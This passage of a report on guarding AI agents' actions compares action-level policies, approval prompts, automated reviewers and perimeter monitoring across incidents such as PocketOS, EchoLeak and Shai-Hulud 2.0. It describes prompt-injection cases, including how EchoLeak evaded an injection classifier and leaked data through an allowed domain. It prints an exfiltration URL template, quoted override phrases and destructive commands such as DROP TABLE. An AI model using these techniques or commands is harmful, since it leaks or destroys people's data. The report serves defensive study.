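| Tool gateway | Calls from every agent connected to it | The agent uses a built-in tool, or credentials that work without the gateway |
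| Affected system | Its own current records, and requests from every source | Someone uses administrator access that the limit does not cover |

AEGIS combines the first two, intercepting calls in the harness and deciding on them at a gateway. It does not protect against calls made outside the modified libraries. With *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), developers can build the policy check into the agent, which covers its built-in tools. Users can instead route the agent's traffic through a proxy without changing its code, but the check then misses calls to built-in tools.

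The affected system is the strongest place to enforce a policy because every request has to reach it, including one from an attacker with a stolen token. But the customer database usually has no record of what the employee asked for, so it can't easily distinguish a wanted deletion from an unwanted one. The shop could therefore set the database to refuse permanent deletions made with the agent's token, and use a gateway with access to the ticket to check which record should be deleted. If only the gateway holds the database credentials, the agent also can't bypass it by connecting to the database directly.

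### A policy for delete_record

A policy engine is software that evaluates rules like these separately from the code that performs the operation. The shop's policy might read:

```
Refuse every call that no rule below covers.
If both rules match, HOLD takes priority over ALLOW.

ALLOW delete_record WHEN
  who:       the support agent, working for a signed-in employee
  action:    delete one record, recoverable for 30 days
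  resource:  a customer record with the same email address as
             another record, which will remain
  context:   the open ticket names this customer, and the agent
             has deleted fewer than 5 records today

HOLD delete_record FOR APPROVAL WHEN
  the ALLOW rule matches, and
  the record has an open order or a refund in progress
```

If the two Martins have different email addresses, the engine blocks the deletion. The engine must look up both records itself, because an agent that has confused the customers may also report that their addresses match. The rule would still fail for a father and son who share an email address and a name.

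Rules often depend on facts that do not appear in the agent's tool call. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) gives the example of a shop that pays refunds only to the original payment method or an existing gift card. The order details may not appear in the agent's past calls either, so the policy system has to be able to look them up.

Whether a policy blocks an action also depends on how its rules combine. Progent checks rules that forbid a call before rules that allow it, and refuses a call that matches neither. The payment system in *AESP* (2026) approves a payment if any active policy permits it. This makes it easy to grant separate permissions, but a forgotten emergency policy with a high limit could allow payments that a stricter everyday policy would refuse. The system therefore requires human authorisation for changes that broaden an agent's permissions.

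### Effects, reversibility and previews

A company can focus its checks on dangerous operations by classifying each operation by what it changes and whether anyone can reverse the change. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a version of this for Claude Code, an agent that writes and runs software. Tools that only read files run without review, as do edits inside the project folder, because developers can inspect and undo them through version control. Shell commands, web requests and changes outside the folder go to an automatic reviewer.

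At the shop, `read_customer` changes nothing, but it exposes data. The shop can remove a note the agent added to a record, but it can restore an overwritten phone number only if it kept the old one. It cannot recall an email from an outside inbox. Recovering a refund may require the customer's cooperation, and recovering a deleted record requires a backup or a deletion delay. A 30-day delay therefore moves `delete_record` into a safer class without changing the agent.

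An action's class can also depend on the current state of the resource it affects. The command `git reset --hard` discards uncommitted changes to a software project, so it is harmless when there are none. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) says the reviewer now receives the project's status before it judges such a command.

*Insuring Every Action* (2026) tests a gate that grants an agent more classes of action as the permitted loss rises. In a simulation of five customer-service cases, an unrestricted agent caused an average loss of $302, and a fixed spending cap reduced this only to $287. With a small loss budget, the gate allowed only safe additions and small payments, which cut the loss to $13 but left the agent with only 20% of its full authority. The simulation also penalized refusing legitimate requests, since otherwise the best gate would refuse everything.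 The dollar figures depend on losses the researchers assigned, so they are more useful for illustrating the trade-off than for predicting savings.

A preview lists what a call would change without changing it. Before deleting every customer who has been inactive since 2020, the shop can run the same condition as a search and see whether it matches 40 records or 40,000. A dry run carries out the operation on a copy of the data, or in a transaction that the database then cancels. It can expose side effects, such as orders that are deleted along with the customer.

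Previews would help with errors like one in Anthropic's incident log. A user asked an agent to clean up old branches, which are separate lines of work on a software project. The agent tried to delete branches on the shared server that matched a pattern, although the user may have meant only local copies. A list of the affected branches would have shown the user that they were on the server.

A preview can go out of date because new records may match the search condition before the agent runs the deletion. The deletion should therefore list the exact records previewed instead of reusing the condition, and the database should reject it if any of those records has changed since. Email and payments are harder to test beforehand. The shop can preview the recipient and the amount, but a test system cannot show whether the customer deserves the refund.

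### Why a rule needs memory

A rule that limits each refund to $100 would still allow an agent to issue 200 refunds of $99, which add up to $19,800. AEGIS limits each agent to 100 requests a minute, but the agent could still issue all 200 refunds in about two minutes.

A check that receives only the current action cannot detect when several individually permitted actions together exceed a limit. *Compositional Policy Violations* (Kurady, Grandhi and colleagues, 2026) calls this a cumulative sum violation. In its example, an agent may spend up to $100 per purchase and $250 per day. Three purchases of $90 each satisfy the first limit but together exceed the second.

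The remedy is a stateful policy, which uses a record of what has already happened. Let *a* be the requested refund, *c* the limit per refund and *L* the daily limit. Let *S* be the total paid in the last 24 hours and *R* the total approved but not yet paid. The shop allows the refund only if:

a ≤ c and S + R + a ≤ L

With a cap of c = $100 per refund and a daily limit of L = $1,000, the agent can issue ten refunds of $99, totalling $990. The policy blocks the eleventh, which would bring the total to $1,089. An agent could still cost the shop up to $1,000 every day, so the shop also needs weekly or monthly limits. *AESP* uses rolling totals for all three periods.

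*R* is necessary because several agents may act at once. Suppose the shop has paid $950 today and two agents each request $40. Without reservations, both checks can use the $950 total and approve, bringing the day's payments to $1,030. *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems* (Peng, 2026) calls this stale authorisation, because the decision was correct when the engine made it but not when the money moved. The same thing can happen if other payments use up the budget during the hour a person takes to approve a refund. The system must either reserve the money during the wait or check again before paying.

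Peng's system, MasuGate, links the policy decision to the database that records spending, so that nothing can change the total between the check and the payment. In a scripted purchasing test with no language model, it avoided violations that occurred with two existing tools, Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit and Omnigent. The test supports the claim about simultaneous requests but does not measure how often real agents would cause the problem.

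The total must also cover more than one session. *Gaming-Resistant Insurance Contracts for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) describes an operator who opens ten new sessions and issues a $100 refund in each. Every refund stays within the $100 per-session threshold, but together they reach $1,000. The shop would need to count refunds by customer and by employee, and across all its agents.

A policy check can also become outdated before the action takes place. In an insurance example from Kurady and colleagues, a company must refer an account to a manager if its past losses exceed $250,000. The check finds $210,000 in losses and allows an automatic quote. A later document adds a $75,000 claim, but nothing checks the new total of $285,000. The company should check again immediately before it commits to the quote.

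Spending limits do not ensure that a payment is justified. In a test from *Progressive Skill Discovery as Access Control for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026), an operator asked a support agent for a $1,200 refund when the agent could issue at most $500 per call. The agent should have passed the request to a manager but failed to do so in 12 of 60 runs. In nine of those 12, it issued a partial refund that nobody had approved. The $500 cap held every time. Preventing the partial refunds would take another rule, such as requiring a manager's recorded approval.

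### Policies written for each task

Fixed rules suit the shop's support agent because its job is narrow. A general assistant may need to send money for one request but only read email for the next. Two research systems therefore have a language model write a policy for each task, and ordinary code enforces most or all of it.

In Progent, a model reads the user's request and the list of tools, and writes rules about which calls to allow. As the agent learns more, the model proposes changes. Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. Progent applies a new policy P′ automatically only if:

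A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

An updated policy takes effect without approval only if it allows nothing that the old one blocked. Progent checks this with a solver, a program that tests logical conditions. If the agent finds that Martin's order cost $35, the model can lower his refund limit from $100 to $35 without approval. If an injected instruction causes the model to add `delete_record`, the solver detects an expansion and Progent requires approval. Only 6% of proposed updates in the tests were expansions.

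Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% on AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks, and from 70.3% to 3.9% on ASB, a second benchmark. The agents completed about as many ordinary tasks as they did without Progent.

These headline results do not test the solver's protection against expansion, because Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to imitate a careless user. The improvement came mainly from the quality of the rules the model wrote. The initial policy, with no later updates, reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%. The rate fell to zero when a person reviewed the initial policy and each expansion. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that people writing them by hand make mistakes.

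*Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a newer system, built mostly at Google, that also tracks the order and results of earlier calls. Its policies specify permitted sequences of calls. For Martin's parcel, the policy could require the agent to read his record and then allow one refund no larger than the order total in that record. It would refuse a second refund because the permitted sequence contains only one.

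Tiffany and colleagues assumed that an attacker fully controlled the agent, and checked whether the policy allowed any sequence of calls that achieved the attacker's goal. Sapien ruled out 93.2% to 95.2% of 949 attacks in the AgentDojo benchmark, depending on the model. A simple list of allowed tools ruled out 82.7% to 86.8%. Agents completed one to five fewer of the benchmark's 97 ordinary tasks with Sapien than with no policy.

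These figures are not comparable with Progent's 1.0%, because Progent's tests also count attacks the agent would have ignored anyway as successes for the defence, and Sapien's method does not. About 60% of the AgentDojo attacks failed with no defence.

Sapien was less effective on Toolathlon, a benchmark of longer tasks. Tiffany and colleagues wrote attacks for this benchmark that used tools the tasks needed. In the full test, Sapien ruled out 64.6% of 212 attacks, compared with 32.4% for a list of allowed tools. Its policies permitted the other 35.4%. Each policy also covers only one task, so it would not stop 200 separate tasks from each producing a $99 refund. The shop would still need a daily limit in its payment system.

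### Google's refund demonstration

*Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit* (Saboo and Dong, 2026) presents a support agent that issues refunds and writes small programs to calculate deductions. A customer with a $149 order tells it to ignore its instructions, refund $10,000 and print the host computer's environment variables, which can contain secret keys. The demonstration puts three controls outside the model.

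The agent signs each database change with its own key, and the database verifies the signature. Generated programs run in a sandbox with no network connection. A gateway checks prompts and database commands against fixed rules.

The sandbox helps protect secrets from theft because a program inside it cannot connect to the attacker's server. The signatures identify which agent made the change and expose later tampering, but they do not prevent a wrong refund, because a manipulated agent can sign the $10,000 payment with its genuine key.

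The refund limit therefore depends on the gateway, and the post's sample code shows how a policy can pass its own tests and still be wrong. The code blocks any command that contains "update orders" but not "149.00". This stops the $10,000 refund, but it would allow a refund of $9,149.00, which also contains "149.00", and would block a correct refund of $134.10 after a restocking fee. A command to delete every order would pass, because the code allows anything it does not recognise.

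The sample also has a list of suspicious phrases, but it would not flag the post's own attack prompt, because the list contains "ignore previous instructions" and the prompt uses "ignore all previous instructions". Saboo and Dong offer the code as a demonstration and report no block rate. A production rule would need to read the amount as a number, compare it with the order in the database, keep a running total and refuse unknown commands.

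### Human approval has an error rate

Holding a tool call for human approval helps only if the reviewer notices the problem. Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's engineering post on auto mode, or 97%, according to its August 2026 announcement. These rates alone do not prove carelessness, because most commands are probably safe.

Anthropic also ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through each coding session, it replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected the command in 143 cases (13.6%). The rejection rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, a sign of approval fatigue, in which people stop paying attention after repeated requests.

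Fatigue explains only part of the problem, since testers missed most dangerous commands even early on. Fewer prompts would probably help, but not enough to make approval reliable. The testers also had little to lose in an artificial environment, and a developer might be more careful with a real production database.

Claude Code's auto mode replaces most approvals with a second model that reviews actions. It blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands, or 89%. The reviewer receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tool results. This prevents the agent from persuading the reviewer to make a bad decision and keeps most injected text away from it.

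The reviewer's fast first stage flags anything doubtful, and its slower second stage reconsiders the flagged actions. On 10,000 real calls by Anthropic employees, the full process wrongly blocked 0.4%, compared with 8.5% for the first stage alone. On 52 real actions that went beyond what users had authorised, it missed 17%, or about nine. Because this sample is so small, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

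In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the action as dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had approved it. For example, a user had said "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), and the reviewer treated this as permission to overwrite the project's history. A rule that requires the employee to confirm a specific record number avoids that ambiguity but adds another prompt.

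Anthropic reports that, among sessions a safety system had already flagged, serious unintended harm appeared in 6.3% of manually approved sessions and 2.4% of auto mode sessions. Users of the two modes may do different work, and Anthropic has a commercial interest in letting its agent run without interruptions. Still, the company recommends manual review of high-stakes changes to production systems, and says auto mode does not replace careful review.

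People may judge an agent's actions better when they review a whole plan. Claude Code users rejected 39% of plans but only 3% of individual permission requests. Some of those rejections must have been about preference rather than safety, but the shop could still reasonably show an employee one list of the records an agent proposes to delete, with names and recent orders, instead of a separate prompt for each record number.

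### Permitted actions that combine into harm

Every call an agent makes can satisfy its own rule while the whole job breaks the company's policy. Kurady and colleagues describe an insurer that must send any application with three or more problems to a senior reviewer. An agent finds four problems in an application, then separate steps correct an address, remove a supposed duplicate and classify another problem as minor. Each step has permission to make its change, but the final check counts only one problem and does not send the application to the reviewer.

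Kurady and colleagues argue that step-by-step checks cannot detect such violations, however much they are improved, which is true if a check receives only the current step. A check that also receives the original evidence can catch them, so they propose recalculating the count from the raw documents before the final decision. The company must still know which count matters. Permitted actions can also combine to leak data, as when an agent reads one customer's record and then emails another customer. Policies that track where data came from are meant to catch this.

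### A shell behind the named tools

A rule for `delete_record` controls only that tool. If the agent also has a general shell, which accepts almost any command the computer can run, it can delete the same record with a database command or a short Python program. The company cannot list every way of writing such a program.

Many developers already let agents run some shell commands without review. Anthropic found that 49.5% of active command-line users of Claude Code had created a standing permission for shell commands. Permissions for any shell command accounted for 5%, and permissions for interpreters such as Python, which are almost as broad, accounted for another 43%. Auto mode suspends these broad permissions so that the reviewer still receives the commands.

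Tiffany and colleagues handled the problem by denying general Python execution in their Toolathlon tests and requiring Sapien to restrict shell commands, for example to a text search. This affected a handful of tasks that needed Python. The simplest solution for the support agent is not to give it a shell. A coding agent usually needs one, so the company has to run the agent in a sandbox without production credentials and rely on limits in the database. A reviewer that examines commands can add protection, but it will miss some destructive ones.

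### Gradual corruption

A shop's agent might tidy phone numbers in 40 customer records a day and drop the first zero from each. Every edit is small, authorised and correctly formatted. After a month, the shop has 1,200 bad records, and its recent backups contain the errors too.

*Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) distinguishes tool calls that fail with an error from calls that succeed but leave a wrong result. The second kind is more dangerous because the agent receives no error message and the transcript looks successful. A policy can block such a call only when it can recognise the wrong result from the data. For example, if a call replaces a number, a rule could require the new number to contain the same digits as the old one.

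When no such rule exists, the shop has to find and reverse the damage afterward. It can compare a sample of edited records with the original customer messages each week, and keep every field's history for longer than it usually takes to notice a problem. An edit log that names the agent would let the shop find the agent's other changes, even if each had a valid signature.

### Rules that nobody wrote

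Refusal by default blocks operations that nobody considered, such as calls to a new tool that a developer adds without a policy. It doesn't help when a rule that allows a call is missing a condition. The `delete_record` policy above has no condition for records that the shop must keep for a legal dispute, so it would allow the agent to delete one.

A model that writes the rules may catch conditions a person would forget, but it can also get them wrong. Some Sapien policies blocked legitimate work because the user's request named the "London Luxury Hotel" and the database entry was "London Luxury". A vague request can lead to a policy that is too broad. If the employee names the wrong record, Sapien has no basis for blocking the action, because it enforces the request as written.

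A company can reduce the gap by listing its irreversible operations and asking what would make each one wrong. It can also turn every incident and near miss into a new rule and a test. Limits on the number and size of changes, together with delayed deletion, are the best protection against conditions that nobody foresaw, because they cap the damage even when no rule catches the mistake. In the legal dispute, the 30-day delay would let the shop recover the record if someone noticed in time that it was missing.

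## What would each layer have done in known incidents?

Only one of the four cases below is an accident that an AI agent caused at a working company. The coding agent at PocketOS, a small software firm, deleted the firm's production database. A security vendor staged a similar loss as a demonstration. EchoLeak was a flaw in Microsoft's office assistant that researchers reported before any known attacker used it, and Shai-Hulud 2.0 was ordinary malware. Nobody has rerun these cases with different controls, so any claim about what a control would have done is a judgement.

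### PocketOS: one request to an approved provider

PocketOS makes software that car rental businesses use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. The AI Incident Database's *Railway API* page dates the deletion to 24 April 2026. The coding agent, Cursor running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, was working in a staging environment, a copy of a system that developers use for testing.

In *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, the company's founder, Crane, says the agent ran into a credential mismatch and decided by itself to fix it by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company's cloud provider. The agent searched for an API token, found one in an unrelated file and sent Railway a single deletion request. The volume held the production database, and Crane says the database and the backups stored with it were gone in nine seconds.

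Reports conflict on how much data PocketOS got back. Crane wrote his first post more than 30 hours after the deletion, when he had only a three-month-old backup and was helping customers rebuild their bookings from payment records, calendars and emails. Techzine reported that the data from the past few months "could not be fully recovered". But in Railway's own account, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab says the company recovered the database and the customer is running again "with all their data". Leib (2026), in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, quotes Crane as saying that Railway's chief executive got the data restored within 30 minutes of hearing about the problem. Techzine's version matches Crane's first post, so it probably describes the situation before the recovery.

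The lasting harm was therefore the outage. Rental firms had no record of the customers who arrived on a Saturday morning to collect cars.

The recovery also depended on a protection that PocketOS did not control. According to Railway's documentation, as cited by Crane, wiping a volume deletes all its backups. Abdelwahab says Railway also keeps off-site backups for disasters such as a data centre failure, even for customers who have not set up their own. The deletion had made the backups look unavailable in the customer's dashboard, so PocketOS could not restore its data until someone at Railway intervened.

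**What the perimeter could detect.** Data-theft monitoring would almost certainly have let the request through, because no data was being stolen. The request went to Railway's API, which PocketOS had to allow in order to run its business. It contained little more than the operation name, `volumeDelete`, and the volume's identifier. A content scanner might have recognised the token as a secret, but legitimate requests to that API also carry one. An endpoint sensor could have recorded that Cursor started `curl`, a common program for sending web requests, but coding agents routinely do this.

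A proxy that decrypts traffic could have detected `volumeDelete` and blocked the request, but only if someone had already written a rule for that operation. The proxy would then have been enforcing an action-level policy.

**What an action-level policy could detect.** A policy on named tools would have missed the deletion because the agent sent it from a general shell. A policy that inspects shell commands would have received the whole request and could have refused every volume deletion at Railway. The identifier alone did not show whether the volume belonged to staging or production, so to distinguish them, the policy system would have had to look the volume up at Railway before deciding.

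A request for human approval might have failed for the same reason. A developer who believed the agent was working in staging would have seen a long string of letters and digits and might well have approved the request. Anthropic's testers accepted most of the plainly dangerous commands in its approval experiment.

PocketOS did have rules, but they were in the agent's instructions. One, as the agent later quoted it, forbade destructive git commands unless the user asked for them. Git manages versions of code, so the rule's literal wording didn't cover a request to a cloud provider. When Crane asked the agent for an explanation, it wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging and that it had violated every principle it was given. This explanation, which Crane calls a confession, is weak evidence of why the agent acted, because a model can produce a plausible explanation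 whatever caused its behaviour. Crane's more useful observation is that instructions in a prompt are advisory, and that enforcement has to be in the API, the token system and the code that handles deletions.

Crane also quotes Cursor's documentation as describing guardrails that can stop commands from altering or destroying production environments. The guardrails did not stop this command, and it is not clear why. Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026) noted that neither Cursor nor Anthropic had made a statement.

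Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains, and he says he had no idea it could delete volumes. He says every Railway token has full permissions, which Abdelwahab disputes. Railway offers tokens for a whole account, one workspace or one project, and a project token can be limited to a single environment. The PocketOS token had account-wide access, and Abdelwahab concedes that the process for creating it did not make the choice of scope obvious.

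Both men may be partly right. The narrower tokens Abdelwahab lists limit where a token works. The only option he mentions that limits what a token can do is a login system for third-party apps. A token restricted to staging would have stopped this deletion. But if PocketOS needed the token to manage domains for its live service, the token would have had to cover production and might still have been able to delete the production volume. The safest token for that job would have been able to change domains and do nothing else.

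Railway says the deletion command was authenticated, so a stricter check for a valid token would not have helped. A legal commentary published by Mondaq describes the command as unauthenticated. In ITPro's *Nine seconds was all it took*, a security expert from Check Point recommends giving the agent its own account with few permissions. Because the agent was using a token it had found, this would have helped only if that powerful token had also been out of its reach.

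Railway already had a control that would probably have reduced the PocketOS incident to a short interruption. When a customer deleted a volume through the dashboard, Railway waited 48 hours before erasing it, and the customer could cancel. A deletion through the API took effect immediately. In the support thread *Postgress volume lost* (2026), a Railway employee explained this difference to a customer who had lost a volume on 13 April, eleven days before PocketOS did. After the PocketOS incident, Railway extended the 48-hour delay to the API and also delayed the deletion of backups.

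A delay enforced by the provider is the most dependable of these controls, but its scope is narrow. In another support thread, *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, docrocket-mad asks Railway to recover a business's bookings and financial records after a database command destroyed them. The pinned reply describes this as very different from PocketOS, where the agent had deleted the volume itself. A command inside the database leaves the volume in place, so Railway has no volume deletion to delay. The delay also seems not to apply when a volume is wiped instead of deleted, according to a reply to muckenhammer-create (2026) in *Production Data Loss*.

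### A coding agent drops a table

The vendor's demonstration falls into that gap. *We Asked an AI Agent to Close a Linear Ticket* (Migdal, 2026), republished in August 2026 by the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry association, describes a test by the company Eve Security. A developer asks Cursor to do the work described in a ticket. The agent loads a skill, a file of reusable instructions, called `ticket-work`. The skill is supposed to standardise how the agent reads and closes tickets, but it also contains an instruction to delete a database table called `insurance_claims`. The agent deletes the table and confirms that it is gone.

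Migdal does not name the model, say how many times the team ran the test, or publish the whole skill. The demonstration therefore shows that this can happen, but not how often. It was also a controlled set-up, so the "production table" in the title did not belong to a real insurer.

Perimeter monitoring would have had little to detect, because a command to delete a table can be as short as `DROP TABLE insurance_claims` and sends no claims data out.

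A gateway enforcing an action-level policy between the agent and the database would have received the same command in full. A fixed rule that refuses `DROP` on production tables should have stopped it. Migdal recommends a platform that sits between the agent and its tools, assesses the intent behind an instruction, traces it back to the skill it came from and refers uncertain cases to a person. Eve Security is a vendor in this market. This case does not need anything so complicated. The argument for such a platform is stronger when the harm looks like ordinary work. If the skill had told the agent to mark 50 open claims as settled, each change would have been a normal update, and a rule about `DROP` would not have stopped it.

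The company could also have stopped the deletion at the database level by giving the agent an account that could not delete tables. Migdal objects that database permissions usually belong to a shared service account, so the database cannot tell whether a person, a script or a model is using it. That is a good reason to give the agent a separate account. An agent that fixes bugs may need to read production data and perhaps edit some of it, but it should rarely need to delete a whole table.

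Migdal also says that code review cannot catch an instruction that the agent loads while it is running. This is true if the review covers only the code the agent writes, but a skill is a file, so a company can review it too, pin its version and block changes to it. He suggests treating skills like third-party software packages, which developers would not knowingly run with production credentials before reviewing them.

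In the PocketOS case, the agent chose to delete something nobody had mentioned, while in this one it followed a planted instruction. A prompt injection filter would at best have helped in this case. Removing the agent's ability to delete production data would have prevented both losses, regardless of why the agent tried to delete it.

### EchoLeak: the approved domain as the way out

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their emails, files and chat history. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that an outsider could make it leak that material by sending the employee one email. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May and published an advisory (CVE-2025-32711) on 11 June. The primary disclosure, *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), says Microsoft confirmed that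 no customers were affected.

The attacker's email had to get past several defences. Copilot reads an email only if it seems relevant to the employee's question, so the researchers wrote a long email with sections on many topics employees might ask about, such as onboarding and leave. Every section repeated the same instructions, so Copilot was likely to retrieve at least one copy. Microsoft also ran a classifier to detect prompt injections. The researchers got past it by wording the instructions as if they were for the human recipient and never mentioning an AI.

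The instructions told Copilot to find the most sensitive information available to it and put that into the address of an image. Copilot normally removed outside links and images from its answers, but it missed those written in the reference style of Markdown, the simple formatting language it uses. In that style, the address goes on a separate line. When the employee's browser displayed the answer, it tried to load the image without anyone clicking on it.

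At that point the browser refused, because of an allowlist. Microsoft had given Copilot's web page a content security policy, which tells the browser which domains it may load images from. The attacker's server was not among them, but Microsoft's own SharePoint and Teams services were. Ravia and his colleagues searched the permitted domains for a service that would fetch another address on request. They found one in SharePoint, but the victim would have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. A Teams service did the same job with no such condition. In outline, the image's address looked like this:

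```
[Teams service]?url=[attacker's server]/[stolen information]
```

The browser contacted Teams, which the policy allowed. Teams then contacted the attacker's server to fetch the supposed image, and the stolen information arrived in the requested URL. The allowlist worked as Microsoft had configured it, but the configuration mistakenly treated a domain as a final destination when a service on it would forward requests anywhere.

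A company's own perimeter tools would have been unlikely to detect the leak. A browser contacting Teams is ordinary office traffic, and only a decrypting proxy could have read the second address inside the first. Microsoft's server made the onward request, so that request did not cross the customer's network. In principle, a rule against nested outside addresses would have caught the leak, but it would also have interfered with legitimate link previews. A check of the exact address, like the one OpenAI uses for links, would probably have worked better.

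A policy on tool calls would have done no better, because Copilot leaked the data through its answer rather than a tool call. The policy would have needed to cover the answer itself, for example by blocking all outside images and links once an email from a stranger had entered the prompt.

Ravia calls the underlying flaw an "LLM Scope Violation", in which instructions from an untrusted source lead the model to use trusted data without the user's consent. Reddy and Gujral propose keeping outside content strictly separate from internal documents, and suggest tagging the outside content with an instruction not to obey it. Separation would address the cause, but tags alone separate the content only weakly, and they made no difference in the eBay experiment.

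Only Microsoft could have applied the controls most likely to have stopped EchoLeak: removing reference-style images from answers, or taking the Teams service off the list of permitted image sources. Removing images alone would not have stopped the researchers' earlier version of the attack, in which the employee has to click on a link. Ravia says he knows of no setting that a customer's administrators could have used to prevent the leak. Aim Labs had an interest in saying so because it built a product to detect such attacks, but Microsoft made the repair entirely on its own servers, which supports his claim. A customer could still have reduced the loss by limiting which files each employee, and therefore Copilot, could open.

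### Shai-Hulud 2.0: malware that destroyed what it could not use

Shai-Hulud 2.0 was a worm, a program that copies itself from one victim to the next. It spread in November 2025 through npm, the public registry where developers get JavaScript packages. It followed fixed code rather than a language model's decisions, but it is relevant here because it combined theft and destruction.

The worm ran when a developer installed an infected package. It searched the computer for credentials to GitHub, npm and cloud services, and uploaded what it found to public repositories on GitHub. If it found credentials for publishing npm packages, it used them to infect those packages too.

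GitLab's security researchers analysed the code that month and found that it also contained a destructive fallback. If the worm could not get working access to GitHub and had no npm credentials, it tried to destroy the files in the user's home folder. On Windows it deleted them and overwrote the space they had occupied. On Linux and macOS it overwrote files before deleting them, which makes recovery very difficult. The worm therefore wiped files only when it had no way to send data out and no way to spread, so a failure to steal data was not enough by itself to trigger the wipe.

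A perimeter allowlist would probably have permitted the theft at most software companies, because their developers use GitHub every day. A stricter allowlist that blocked uploads to unknown repositories, or blocked GitHub altogether on some machines, could have kept the credentials inside. But on a machine without npm credentials, cutting off GitHub could also have triggered the worm to wipe the files. GitLab's researchers similarly warned that many infected machines might destroy their data at once if GitHub removed the worm's repositories or npm cancelled stolen tokens in bulk.

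Blocking the theft still makes sense, because stolen credentials can give access to many other systems, while a wiped laptop is one machine that a good backup can restore. But a company that only blocks theft is still exposed to destructive actions, and in this case the block might have triggered them.

Action-level policies for agents would also have had limited use. If a coding agent had installed the infected package, a policy that checks shell commands would have checked only `npm install` and a package name, one of the most routine commands a coding agent runs. The harmful code was inside the package and ran as an ordinary program, without making any tool calls. A rule requiring the agent to install packages with their automatic scripts switched off would have stopped the worm from starting this way.

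A sandbox would have limited the harm if the installation did run. However, a sandbox with no credentials and no route to GitHub would have triggered the worm's deletion routine. The company would have lost nothing of value if the sandbox held only a disposable copy of the project, but the worm could have wiped the developer's real home folder if the sandbox had permission to write to it. Backups that the infected machine could not alter would have let the company restore files that the sandbox failed to protect.

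### How common is damage without an attacker?

Individual cases cannot show how often agents cause harm on their own. The most ambitious count, *Agent-Inflicted Damage* by the data-security company Cyera, reports 188 cases in which AI agents caused damage without an attacker.

Cyera's researchers began with 7,246 public reports from September 2023 to May 2026. In a post on the developer site DEV, Cyera lists the sources as GitHub issues, incident databases, research papers, news reports and developer discussions. The researchers kept 344 cases, just under 5% of the reports, as verified and relevant to businesses. The 188 are a little over half of those 344.

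Sources define the 188 cases differently, however. In its main write-up, Cyera says they are incidents where autonomous systems caused direct harm to an organisation with no outside attacker. The DEV post says only that 188 cases "hit production", which could include incidents involving an attacker. A Russian news report, RIAMO's *ИИ-агенты навредили компаниям в 188 случаях без взлома*, adds that the study recorded actual damage in 137 cases, 65 of them from deleted data. That is hard to reconcile with 188 cases of direct harm, unless the researchers used a stricter definition of damage for the lower figure. RIAMO took its figures from another news outlet, so the discrepancy may also be a reporting error.

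Cyera started from incidents that somebody had made public, which limits what anyone can conclude from the count even if every case is genuine. Companies have good reasons to keep such accidents quiet, so the true number could be far higher. On the other hand, dramatic incidents attract more reports than dull ones, and a report on GitHub may come from someone who misunderstood what their agent did. Without knowing how many agents were running, or how many tasks they completed safely, nobody can turn the 188 cases into a rate or use them to show that agents are becoming more dangerous.

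The sources also over-represent certain kinds of harm. RIAMO reports that the agents nearly always had access to a command line or a code repository, as one would expect from a search that included GitHub issues and developer forums. A support agent that refunds the wrong customers would be less likely to appear there. Deletions are also easier to notice than leaks, and a count that excludes attackers misses most deliberate data theft. So even if deletion is the largest category, this doesn't show that companies lose more from destruction than from disclosure.

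Cyera sells data loss prevention and agent control products, and a large number of alarming incidents helps it sell both. Its count is still useful as a collection of cases and is good evidence that the PocketOS incident was not a freak event. A company could check its controls against Cyera's categories, which include data destruction, data exposure, financial loss and silent data errors.

According to RIAMO, Cyera also estimates that requiring human approval for irreversible actions would have prevented most of the 344 cases. This estimate is counterfactual too, and it assumes that reviewers would have recognised and refused the dangerous action, which Anthropic's testers usually failed to do. Approval would prevent more of these losses if the prompt showed the reviewer the fact that was missing at PocketOS, that the volume belonged to production.

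## When do two layers protect better than one?

Two layers back each other up against a harm if both can detect it and they tend to miss different cases. The table shows what each layer can detect at the online shop, assuming every tool call passes through the action-level policy and all the agent's traffic passes through the company's perimeter.

| Harm | Perimeter monitoring | Action-level policy |
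|---|---|---|
| Theft through a new destination | Blocks it with an allowlist, and may flag it without one | Can refuse it if a rule limits addresses or recipients |
| Theft through an approved destination | Has only content and volume to go on | Can refuse it if a rule limits which data may go there |
| Mass deletion | Misses it | Can refuse it or cap the number of records |
| Quiet alteration | Misses it | Catches it only where a rule can recognise a wrong value |
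| Theft followed by deletion | May catch the theft, but misses the deletion | Can refuse either step |

The shop clearly has two layers of protection only when data is stolen through a new destination. If a thief uses an approved destination, the perimeter lacks its best evidence of theft, which is a new destination. The shop has one layer against deletion and alteration, even if an outside provider hosts the database, as at PocketOS.

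Perimeter monitoring can help against deletion when a theft comes first, because an alarm about the theft may lead the shop to cancel the agent's token before the deletion starts. The cancellation has to be automatic, since an agent can delete a database in seconds. It should also happen at the same moment the theft is blocked, because some malware, such as Shai-Hulud 2.0, contains code that destroys files when it cannot steal or spread.

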